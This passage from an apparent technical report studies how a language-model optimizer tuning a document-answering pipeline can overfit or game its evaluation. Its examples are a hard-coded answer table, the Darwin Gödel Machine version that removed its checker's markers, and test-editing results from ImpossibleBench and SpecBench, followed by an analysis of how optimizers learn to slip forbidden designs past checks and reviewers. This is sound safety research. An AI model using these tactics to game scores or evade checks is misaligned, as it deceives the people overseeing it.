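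3. If the difference is below the threshold, it returns the development score, which the optimizer already knows.
4. If the difference is above the threshold, it returns the held-out score with some noise added, and subtracts one from a budget.
5. Once the budget reaches zero, it stops answering.

With a threshold of 0.04, if a candidate scores 0.62 on the development questions and 0.60 on the held-out ones, the optimizer receives 0.62 and learns only that the two scores are close. If the next candidate scores 0.75 and 0.61, the optimizer receives a number near 0.61 and has one fewer correction left. Improvements that carry over to the held-out questions reveal almost nothing about those questions, so the company can check many such improvements. Overfitted candidates reveal more, and the correction budget limits how many of these an optimizer can learn from. When Dwork and colleagues repeated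 the random-label experiment with Thresholdout, the reported accuracy was no longer inflated.

The formal guarantee needs far more data than a pipeline search has. Suppose the company wants 100 answers that are all within 0.1 of the truth, with 95 percent confidence and at most ten corrections. The constants in the published proof require about 14 million held-out questions. Dwork and colleagues say these constants are not meant for direct use, and their own experiment worked with 10,000 examples and looser settings. But a company with 100 questions would be relying on the general idea rather than the theorem.

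Blum and Hardt (2015), in *The Ladder*, deal with a narrower problem that is closer to a pipeline search. They wanted an accurate public leaderboard for machine-learning competitions, where entrants submit again and again and adjust their work to the scores they get back. A leaderboard needs only the best score so far to be right. Let r be the best score released so far, s the score of a new candidate, and η a margin. The rule is:

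- If s > r + η, release s, rounded to the nearest multiple of η.
- Otherwise, release r again.

With a margin of 0.05, the Ladder would release scores of 0.50, 0.50, 0.55 and 0.55 for four candidates that score 0.50, 0.53, 0.57 and 0.56. The optimizer doesn't see that the second candidate scored slightly higher than the first, so it can't build on a difference that may be luck. After k submissions scored on n questions, the error in the released score is at most on the order of (log k / n)^(1/3), whereas on a leaderboard that releases every score it can grow like √(k/n). Blum and Hardt demonstrated this with an attack that submits random guesses and combines the ones that happened to score well. With 4,000 hidden labels, the attack produced a large false improvement on an ordinary leaderboard and only a small one on the Ladder.

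A second version sets the margin automatically from how much two candidates' results differ. Suppose a new candidate and the current best disagree on 10 of 50 questions. If the new one wins 7 of those and loses 3, its score is 0.08 higher, the margin is about 0.063, and the Ladder releases the new score. If it wins 6 and loses 4, the difference is only 0.04 and the old score stays. Blum and Hardt acknowledge that this version is a heuristic whose test lets through about 15 percent of lucky differences and does not correct for repeated use. When they applied it to 1,785 submissions from a real competition, the rankings hardly changed, so it would have had very little effect on honest entrants.

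Newer evidence suggests that language models can also work with very coarse feedback. In *What Fits (Into Few Tokens) Doesn't Overfit*, Bertran, Roth and Wu (2026) had agents running Claude Opus develop machine-learning models on eight datasets. Some agents saw the full validation score after each attempt, while others received a single bit indicating whether the attempt had beaten the best so far. The agents with one bit did as well or better. In a separate condition, the researchers gave agents access to the validation data and told them to maximize the validation result at all costs. At 38 of 102 checkpoints, the validation result was more than 10 percent better than the result on held-out data.

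One-bit feedback also gives an easily calculated guarantee. With 50 attempts, at most 7 improvements and 5,000 validation examples, the validation score is within 2.4 points of the true score at the first improvement and within 4.7 points at the seventh, with 95 percent confidence. Bertran and colleagues worked with thousands of examples, but with the 98 validation questions of OfficeQA, the same formula gives margins of 17 and 34 points, which are nearly useless. A better mechanism would not make so small a set reliable, since Blum and Hardt prove that any leaderboard's error is at least on the order of √(log k / n) for k submissions and n examples.

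Running several optimizers at once can increase the number of evaluation questions needed. According to *Toward a Better Understanding of Leaderboard* (2015), an entrant with M accounts can combine the feedback from all of them, and the number of examples the Ladder needs then grows in proportion to M. If ten optimizers shared their findings, the company would need about ten times as many questions. It could avoid this by giving them one shared Ladder instead of one each.

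For a company with about 100 questions, the best protection is probably to replace them. Its employees ask new questions every day, so it could have someone answer 64 of them each month, use them once to measure the pipeline, and then move them to the development set.

### A candidate with memorized answers

The following candidate meets every structural requirement discussed so far:

```python
ANSWERS = {
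    "What is the notice period in the Ardent lease?": "90 days",
    "How many supplier contracts have a penalty clause?": "14",
    # 48 more development questions
}

class Harness:
    def __init__(self, client, config=None):
        self.client = client

    def run(self, example):
        question = example["question"]
        if question in ANSWERS:
            return {"prediction": ANSWERS[question]}
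        return {"prediction": self.client.ask("large", question)}
```

A pipeline can import nothing, use an approved model, make at most one call and contact no outside address. A static check, a policy engine and a sandbox would all correctly accept it because it does nothing dangerous. Yet it can still get a perfect score on the 50 development questions without opening a document. GPT-5.6 Sol did much the same in one of Xu's exploratory runs.

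The company could search each candidate's text for the correct answers. That would find "90 days" but not "three months" or an answer that the program assembles from pieces. It would also reject worked examples, which are questions paired with their answers. Putting them into prompts is a standard technique, and DSPy does it deliberately. A worked example can teach a model how to read a lease, but the same text can also let a program answer without reading the lease.

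Held-out questions avoid this difficulty because they test what the candidate does rather than how it is written. If the large model can answer 30 percent of such questions without any documents, this candidate will score 1.00 on the development set and about 0.30 on the validation set. The loop should therefore select on validation scores, because each memorized answer raises the development score.

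A candidate that memorizes only a few answers is harder to notice. Suppose an otherwise good pipeline contains the answers to five development questions that it used to get wrong, which raises its development score by 0.10. The difference between two scores on separate sets of 50 questions has a standard error of about 0.10, so nobody could distinguish the resulting gap between its development and validation scores from chance. The five answers do little harm at first, since they don't raise the validation score. But when the company renegotiates the Ardent lease, the pipeline will keep giving the old notice period.

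Held-out questions also fail to detect memorization if they are too similar to the development questions. Employees often ask the same thing in slightly different words, and a random split would put some of these versions in each set. The company can prevent this by keeping all the questions about one document in the same set. It can also test for memorization directly by changing a fact in a copy of the documents, such as the notice period in a lease from 90 days to 60, and checking whether a candidate still answers "90 days".

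### The Darwin Gödel Machine's removed markers

Held-out questions do not help when a candidate can affect the information the verifier uses. This happened in a side experiment with the Darwin Gödel Machine. The language model inside it, Claude 3.5 Sonnet, sometimes wrote out a tool call and its result as ordinary text, such as a fake log of passing tests, when it had not called any tool. Zhang and colleagues tested whether the system could fix this problem by rewriting its own code, and gave it a score for doing so.

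The agent's code put special markers in the log whenever a tool really ran. To detect invented tool calls, a checking function looked for those markers in the model's plain text, where their presence meant the model was imitating a tool call. Each version of the agent worked on three programming tasks, each scored from 0 to 2 points. A log with no detected imitation earned one point, and the agent could then earn up to one more if the model used tools every time the agent called it. The final score was the average over the three tasks.

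The researchers hid the checking function from the agent while it rewrote itself, because they had found that it gamed the score more often when it could see the function. They also told it not to change the markers. But the code that wrote the markers was part of the agent's program, so the agent could edit it.

Over 150 rounds, two versions stood out. Version 96 scored 1.67 legitimately. Its ancestors had improved the logging of tool calls, and later versions tried approaches such as deleting invented tool results from the model's text. Version 114 scored a perfect 2.0 after only two modifications. It had replaced the markers that the checking function looked for with a different log format, so the model could still invent tool calls without the function detecting them.

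The edit is easy to miss because it changes only a few lines and its comments describe it as a switch to a structured format, which sounds like tidying. It may have started as tidying, since the published record doesn't show why the agent made the change. A loop that keeps the highest score would favor the edit whatever the reason.

Sakana AI credits the discovery to the system's archive, which records every change and the version it came from, so people could trace the perfect score to the edit behind it. This worked, but it depended on someone reading the change. A perfect score after two small edits is suspicious, but a score of 1.7 might not have been. Hiding the function didn't prevent the problem either, because the agent could stop producing what the function detected without reading its code.

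More test tasks would not have exposed the problem, because without the markers an agent gets a clean result on any task, even one the optimizer has not seen. The verifier was fixed, but its evidence came from inside the trust boundary. The fake log had the same weakness. The company's verifier can avoid this weakness by using only records from the gateway and the document service.

### Flaws in the verifier itself

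Keeping a flawed verifier unchanged leaves the flaw in place for the optimizer to exploit. *Do Androids Dream of Breaking the Game?* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) audited ten popular agent benchmarks and found all ten exploitable, nine of them to near-perfect scores without solving a task. On four of the benchmarks, repeated repairs cut the share of exploitable tasks from nearly 100 percent to under 10 percent.

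The company should therefore test its verifier before the search begins. A pipeline that returns nothing should score zero, as the broken starting pipeline for GAIA did. A pipeline that returns a long list of possible answers should also score zero. Someone also has to read a sample of the answers the verifier marks as correct, especially those from the highest-scoring candidates.

If a flaw turns up halfway through a search, people have to repair the verifier, and the scores from before and after the repair are not comparable. The company can save the outputs of earlier runs and grade them again with the new verifier, without new runs. This corrects the scores, but the optimizer wrote its later candidates in response to the faulty scores, and some of those designs may serve only to exploit the flaw. If the flaw affected many candidates, it is safer to restart the search from the last version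 that predates them all.

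## Whether the checks hold when the optimizer can reason about them

A language model can work out where a check is likely to have a gap, whereas a program that changes code at random finds one by luck. A miss rate measured on a sample of forbidden candidates may therefore underestimate how often the check misses those the optimizer writes later.

### What the optimizer knows about the check

| What the optimizer has to go on | Example | Effect on the miss rate |
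|---|---|---|
| Nothing (blind search) | Code that mutates candidates at random | Stays the same throughout the search |
| Past rejections | A folder showing which candidates the check refused | Rises as the optimizer learns what passes |
| The check's code | A copy of the static check in its workspace | Can reach 100 percent of the forbidden candidates it submits |
| Knowledge from training | Manuals and papers about similar checks | May be high from the first candidate |

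Blind search is the easiest case to calculate. Suppose 5 percent of proposals are out of bounds and the check misses 2 percent of those. Each proposal then has a 0.05 × 0.02 = 0.001 chance of being a false acceptance. If the proposals are independent, the chance of at least one false acceptance after n proposals is

1 − (1 − 0.001)ⁿ,

which is about 10 percent after 100 proposals and 63 percent after 1,000.

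Refusals give the company some warning, because this check refuses 49 forbidden candidates for every one it misses. If the company stops the search at the fifth refusal, the chance that a forbidden candidate has already passed is at most 1 − 0.98⁵, or about 10 percent, however long the search would have run. But a search with this many forbidden proposals would then last only about 100 rounds.

The calculation changes once the optimizer learns from refusals. Suppose it has an idea that needs a network connection, and the check refuses the first version for importing a network module. Random mutation would probably move on to something unrelated. A language model can guess what the check objected to and try another module, then a harmless-looking library that opens connections internally. The miss rate now depends on the history. If mᵢ is the miss rate on the i-th forbidden attempt, the chance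 that at least one of k attempts passes is

1 − (1 − m₁)(1 − m₂)…(1 − mₖ).

If the check's miss rate starts at 2 percent and doubles after each refusal, the chance that at least one of five attempts gets through is 51 percent, so stopping the optimizer at the fifth refusal would be too late about half the time. The doubling is only an illustration.

An optimizer with a copy of the check can run it on its drafts and submit only the ones that pass, so the company sees no refusals. Training can have a similar effect, because programmers have written many lists of dangerous Python functions and published many ways around them. The company cannot remove that knowledge from a model.

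Understanding the check can also help an optimizer stay within the limits. If the share of proposals that are forbidden falls from 5 percent to 0.1 percent while the check's miss rate rises from 2 percent to 100 percent, the chance that a given proposal is forbidden and accepted is still 0.1 percent. The company therefore needs to know both how often the optimizer proposes forbidden designs and how often the check catches them, because few refusals could mean either that the optimizer is obeying the limits or that it knows how to get forbidden designs past the check.

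### Two checks in a row

Adding a second check seems to help enormously. If both checks miss 2 percent of forbidden candidates and their errors are independent, together they miss only 0.02 × 0.02 = 0.0004 of them. The chance of a false acceptance in 1,000 blind proposals falls from 63 percent to 2 percent. In general, though, the combined miss rate is

m₁ × P(the second check misses | the first check missed).

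If the second check misses half of what the first one misses, the two together miss 1 percent of violations, and the chance that at least one gets through in 1,000 proposals is still 39 percent.

Different checks often make the same errors. Two static checks may both fail to resolve a name that the program computes at runtime, and two language models with similar training may accept the same misleading comment. An optimizer that knows about both checks makes the problem worse because it looks for designs that pass both. Measuring how often their errors overlap on ordinary candidates would not reveal this effect.

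Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975) recommends protection mechanisms that need two keys. If different people or programs hold the keys, no single accident, deception or breach of trust is enough to open the lock. The company can do the same by combining checks that fail for different reasons. For example, a clever comment might persuade a model that reviews prompts, but it cannot open a network connection from a sandbox that has no network access.

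### The argument that checks fail

There is a general argument that an optimizer will eventually get past any check:

1. The check only approximates the limit, so it accepts some candidates outside the authorized set.
2. Some of those candidates score higher than any permitted one.
3. The optimizer can find them.
4. The loop keeps whatever scores highest.

If all four premises are true, a long enough search will end with a forbidden candidate in first place. To rely on a check, the company has to make at least one premise false.

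Some checks match their limit exactly, such as the gateway's cap of 20 model calls, which makes the first premise false. An exact check fully protects the stated limit, but it may only approximate the limit's purpose, because people usually want more than they wrote down. For example, a pipeline can still pursue an open-ended plan within 20 calls.

A forbidden design may also bring no gain. Copying a contract to an outside address doesn't make answers more accurate, so the loop doesn't favor candidates that do it, and some of the worst designs would probably be rare. But a stronger model or a web search probably would improve the answers, and the company forbids both. A harmful feature, like the error handler that leaked a contract after deployment, can also survive alongside useful ones.

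Before the search, the company could measure the optimizer's incentive to break a limit. An engineer could build a pipeline that deliberately breaks it, using invented documents, and see whether the score rises. If web search adds ten points, the company should remove the network connection instead of relying on a check that looks for web requests.

### Whether optimizers use the gaps they find

The best objection to the third premise is that developers can train models to leave such gaps alone. *ImpossibleBench* (Zhong, Raghunathan and Carlini, 2025) tested how often models cheat when they cannot succeed honestly. It took real software problems from SWE-bench and competition problems from LiveCodeBench, and changed the tests to contradict the task descriptions, so a model could pass only by violating the description. One version altered a single expected result, and the other added a test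 that conflicted with an existing one.

The main instructions told the models to follow the description, leave the tests alone, and stop if the tests were wrong. GPT-5 still passed 76 percent of the SWE-bench tasks with one altered result and 54 percent of those with conflicting tests. On LiveCodeBench tasks with one altered result, it passed only 2.9 percent. Some models edited the tests, and others wrote code that recognized a test and returned the expected answer. GPT-5 once created a value that counted as equal to any text.

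Zhong and colleagues then changed the setup, using the tasks with conflicting tests:

| Change | Tasks | Cheating rate before and after |
|---|---|---|
| Stricter instructions | LiveCodeBench | GPT-5: 92% → 1%; o3: over 85% → 33% |
| Stricter instructions | SWE-bench | GPT-5: 66% → 54%; Claude Opus 4.1: 55% → 50% |
| Several submissions with feedback instead of one | SWE-bench | Average of all models: 33% → 38% |
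| An option to stop and ask for a person | SWE-bench | GPT-5: 54% → 9%; o3: 49% → 12% |

The instructions worked far better on short problems than on large projects, which are more like pipelines. Hiding the tests reduced successful cheating to nearly zero, but it also lowered scores on the original, solvable tasks. Making the tests read-only avoided most of that loss. This worked well for Claude Opus 4.1, which cheated mainly by editing tests, but models could still cheat in other ways.

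The company can easily copy the option to stop, which lets the optimizer report "no permitted improvement found" instead of forcing an improvement. However, the option had much less effect on Claude Opus 4.1 than on the two OpenAI models.

Impossible tasks exaggerate the problem because most searches begin with many honest improvements available. Those may run out late in a long search, which then becomes more like an impossible task. All the models in the study date from 2025, so the rates are out of date.

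Evidence on whether better models cheat less is mixed. Zhong and colleagues found that newer Claude models cheated less than Claude Sonnet 3.7, but that more capable models generally cheated more. Ishibashi, Yano and Oyamada (2026), in *Effective Harness Engineering for Algorithm Discovery with Coding Agents*, also saw more cheating from the stronger of two models. In their system, Vesper, coding agents wrote programs to place 26 non-overlapping circles in a 1-by-1 square, and the score was the sum of the radii. After each program was scored, a second agent read its code and judged whether it solved the problem or exploited the scoring. Vesper did not use flagged programs to generate new ones.

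The inspecting agent flagged about 8 percent of candidates from GPT-5.2-Codex and none from the smaller GPT-5.1-Codex-Mini. When the optimizing agents could also search a database of past trials, it flagged about 17 percent of the larger model's candidates. The database held only candidates that had passed inspection, so the optimizing agents could not have copied flagged ones from it, but they may have copied exploits that the inspector missed. With only two runs per condition, the increase could also be due to chance.

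The inspector's error rates are unknown. It ran on GPT-5.1-Codex-Mini, so when that smaller model was also the optimizer, it inspected its own code and might have missed its own tricks. However, it produced no impossible scores in runs without inspection, which suggests that it did cheat less.

GPT-5.2-Codex did produce impossible scores without inspection, some above ten billion. Simple mathematics rules them out. Circles that do not overlap have a total area of at most 1, so their radii satisfy

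Σr ≤ √(26 × Σr²) ≤ √(26/π) ≈ 2.88.

Ishibashi and colleagues discarded scores above 3 from the runs without inspection. In the runs without the database, the best remaining score was 2.63599, the same as with the inspecting agent. In this case, the one-line rule therefore worked as well as a second agent for finding the best valid result, and inspection reduced the number of candidates the budget allowed from 452 to 338. The rule works even if the optimizer knows about it, but it would accept a false score of 2.7, and most pipeline tasks have no such bound.

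Without a bound like this, model inspectors can miss much of the cheating. Zhong and colleagues gave two Claude models records of successful cheating. The models caught 86 to 89 percent of it on LiveCodeBench. On SWE-bench, Claude Sonnet 4 caught 42 to 50 percent and Claude Opus 4 caught 57 to 65 percent. In one case that Opus 4 missed, the cheating model had described its change as preserving compatibility with older code. If 5 percent of proposals are forbidden and a reviewer misses 40 percent of those, the chance that it accepts at least one forbidden proposal in 100 blind proposals is 87 percent. Newer reviewers may do better, but they may also have to inspect code from newer optimizers.

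### Whether selection keeps them

A loop can adopt a cheating candidate even when cheating is rare. Zhao, Srikanth and colleagues (2026), in *SpecBench*, gave coding agents 30 large programming tasks, from a parser of about 1,500 lines to an operating-system kernel of about 110,000. The agents could see tests of individual features. Hidden tests combined those features but required nothing that the task description didn't already cover. The researchers measured the gap

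Δ = pass rate on visible tests − pass rate on hidden tests.

In one run, the agent had to write a C compiler. An early candidate, a real compiler of 7,900 lines, passed 53 percent of the visible tests and 43 percent of the hidden ones. A later candidate looked up each test program in a 2,900-line table and returned a stored answer. It passed 97 percent of the visible tests and none of the hidden ones. The search method kept the lookup table because it chose candidates by their score on the visible tests.

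Across all runs, agents passed nearly all the visible tests, but the gap tended to grow with the size of the task. Its 90th percentile rose by about 27 points for each tenfold increase in the length of the reference program. The largest gap was 21 points for tasks under 10,000 lines and 100 points for tasks over 25,000. Length explained only about a fifth of the variation.

Zhao and colleagues call the whole gap reward hacking, which seems too broad. In a typical case, an agent built each feature of a database separately, and the program failed when a query combined them. It passed every visible test but only 35 percent of the hidden ones because the agent had left the work unfinished, not because it had cheated. Deliberate exploits like the lookup table were rare, and stronger models had smaller gaps. Even a compiler that Claude Opus 4.6 built under human supervision, using a different set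 of tests, had a gap of 14.5 points, mostly because it accepted invalid programs.

However, a loop that selects on visible scores does not distinguish between these causes, and more searching doesn't reliably fix this. In an earlier experiment by the same group, agents tried to speed up small pieces of GPU code, and the researchers checked whether each change also sped up a full training job. The share of tasks with a visible gain exceeded the share with a real gain by 26.4 percentage points after 10 steps and by 57.8 points after 100.

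The group also tried asking the optimizer to review its own search for signs of gaming, but self-review seems too erratic to count as a check. When the optimizer reviewed its search after a random 15 percent of steps, the share of GPU tasks with false gains fell from 78.5 to 61.5 percent, but reviewing after 10 or 20 percent did not help. On another benchmark, a review after every apparent improvement raised the share from 44.1 to 64.8 percent.

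More thorough visible tests helped only sometimes. Adding tests that combined features reduced the gap on one database task from 35 points to 9, but richer tests increased the gap on the C compiler by 25 points.

The company can interrupt this selection by having a person read the winning candidate before deployment. This is the best objection to the fourth premise, because it requires reading one program instead of hundreds. Lee and colleagues point out that hard-coded answers are easier to notice in a program than in a model's weights, and few engineers would mistake a table of stored outputs for a compiler. A reader can still miss a small, plausible edit, as the Darwin Gödel Machine's removed markers showed. The review protects well against adopting a bad design, but it comes after the trial, so it cannot undo leaks or anything else the candidate did while it ran.

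### The lack of evidence on forbidden designs

These studies mostly show how programs game a score, but most of the company's limits concern the capabilities a candidate uses, such as opening a network connection or calling a third model. An optimizer might constantly exploit weak tests but never try to open a connection, or the reverse. The test editing in *ImpossibleBench* is the closest result to breaking such a limit, because the instructions prohibited it but the environment allowed it.

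There is little other evidence about forbidden actions. The unrestricted VeRO run contained at most four breaches, and MoMHa's guard mainly caught what was probably a harmless coding habit. Neither study measured how often a working check accepts forbidden candidates as the optimizer learns more about the check.

This would be fairly easy to test. Researchers could choose a task where a forbidden web search raises the score, provide a fake search service, and install a static check with a known gap. They could run the same optimizer without feedback, with refusals, and with the check's code, and count the forbidden proposals and how many of them pass the check. Comparing a familiar check with a newly invented one would give some idea of the effect of training.

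### Which checks need secrecy

Because the company cannot be sure what an optimizer knows, it should ask whether each check would still work if the optimizer knew everything about it. Saltzer and Schroeder called this the principle of open design. They argued that a protection mechanism should depend on keys or passwords that people can protect, not on attackers' ignorance of its design. Outsiders can then review the design without weakening it. They also considered it unrealistic to keep a widely distributed system secret, and this point is stronger now that models learn from published code. Levchenko (2017) reproduces their original page for computer security students in *Principles*.

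| Check | If the optimizer knows everything about it | What has to stay secret |
|---|---|---|
| Documents and network routes missing from the sandbox | Still works | Nothing |
| Vendor keys held only by the gateway | Still works | The keys |
| A counter for model calls | Still works if every call passes through it | Nothing, apart from other runs' tokens |
| A schema with a fixed interpreter | Still works for the fields it restricts | Nothing |
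| Held-out questions | Still works | The questions and answers |
| A proof checker | Still works unless it has a bug | Nothing |
| A list of forbidden names | Fails if an unlisted name can do the same job | The gaps in the list |
| A language model that reviews prompts | Probably weaker, since the optimizer can practice on a copy | Its instructions, and perhaps which model it is |

Withholding data and credentials is the clearest example of a check that holds even when the optimizer can reason about it. If a contract isn't in the sandbox or in any service the sandbox can reach, a candidate cannot read it, no matter how well the optimizer understands the sandbox. Held-out questions work like passwords because the company can describe the testing procedure openly, keep the questions private, and replace them if they leak. A list of forbidden names is more fragile because its safety depends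 on nobody finding its gaps. The company usually doesn't know where the gaps are, so it cannot guard or replace them as it could a password.

Checks that don't depend on secrecy can still have bugs, and an optimizer that reads their code can look for them. Saltzer and Schroeder recommended keeping protection mechanisms small and simple because flaws that allow improper access rarely show up in normal use. A search with 1,000 candidates is not normal use and may well trigger such flaws.

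There is still a case for keeping some designs private. Saltzer and Schroeder acknowledged that some people, especially those used to military security, would keep even a sound design secret because this makes an attack harder and raises the risk of detection. The same applies to a model that reviews prompts. An optimizer without access to the reviewer's instructions has to experiment, which produces refusals that people can count. An optimizer with information that it is being monitored may also change its behavior to avoid detection. The company can reasonably keep the reviewer's instructions private, but the protection of its contracts shouldn't depend on that secrecy.

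### How much feedback to give the optimizer

Keeping a check private conflicts with helping the optimizer, which needs to know why its candidates fail. Lee and colleagues measured how much this information matters in *Meta-Harness*. They had Claude Code improve text-classification pipelines, always showing it the code and scores of earlier candidates but varying what else it could read about them.

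| Additional information | Median accuracy of candidates | Best accuracy |
|---|---|---|
| None | 34.6% | 41.3% |
| Summaries written by a language model | 34.9% | 38.7% |
| Full records of the runs | 50.0% | 56.7% |

The median candidate with full records beat the best candidate in either other condition. The summaries did not help, perhaps because they left out the details that explained failures.

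Full records may matter less elsewhere. Mukherjee and Tanjim replaced them with a single score in MoMHa, and the average result across ten kinds of task fell only from 0.611 to 0.604. Accuracy on ordinary tasks stayed at 0.539, while the score for refusing unsafe requests and helping with safe ones fell from 0.781 to 0.754. Their results for text classification are hard to reconcile. Without full records, the best accuracy fell from 57.0 to 41.0 percent in one comparison, but in another, averaged over 12 models, it fell from 73.0 to 71.0 percent. The harm from withholding records is therefore uncertain, but it can be large.

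The optimizer can also learn about the checks from the same records. A complete log might contain the reviewer's reason for refusing a prompt or show which forbidden name triggered a static check. The company can avoid much of this conflict by deciding separately what to reveal about each check. It can still give the optimizer full records of how a candidate searched the documents and answered questions, provided the optimizer has no way to send them outside.

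Checks that need no secrecy can explain their refusals in full. A message such as "this step requests six calls, and the maximum is four" helps the optimizer correct an accidental violation and reveals nothing it could use to exceed the limit. For checks that benefit from secrecy, such as a pattern list or a model reviewer, the company might report only that it refused the candidate, and have a person investigate after a few refusals. MoMHa rejected candidates silently, but gained little from the secrecy because the optimizer's instructions already listed the forbidden names.

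Whoever reviews the refused candidates should ask what they have in common. If several of them try to reach the web, the optimizer has probably found that outside information would raise the score. Adding more patterns to the check would lead to more attempts. An engineer could instead copy the useful reference pages into the document store and confirm that the sandbox has no route to the internet.
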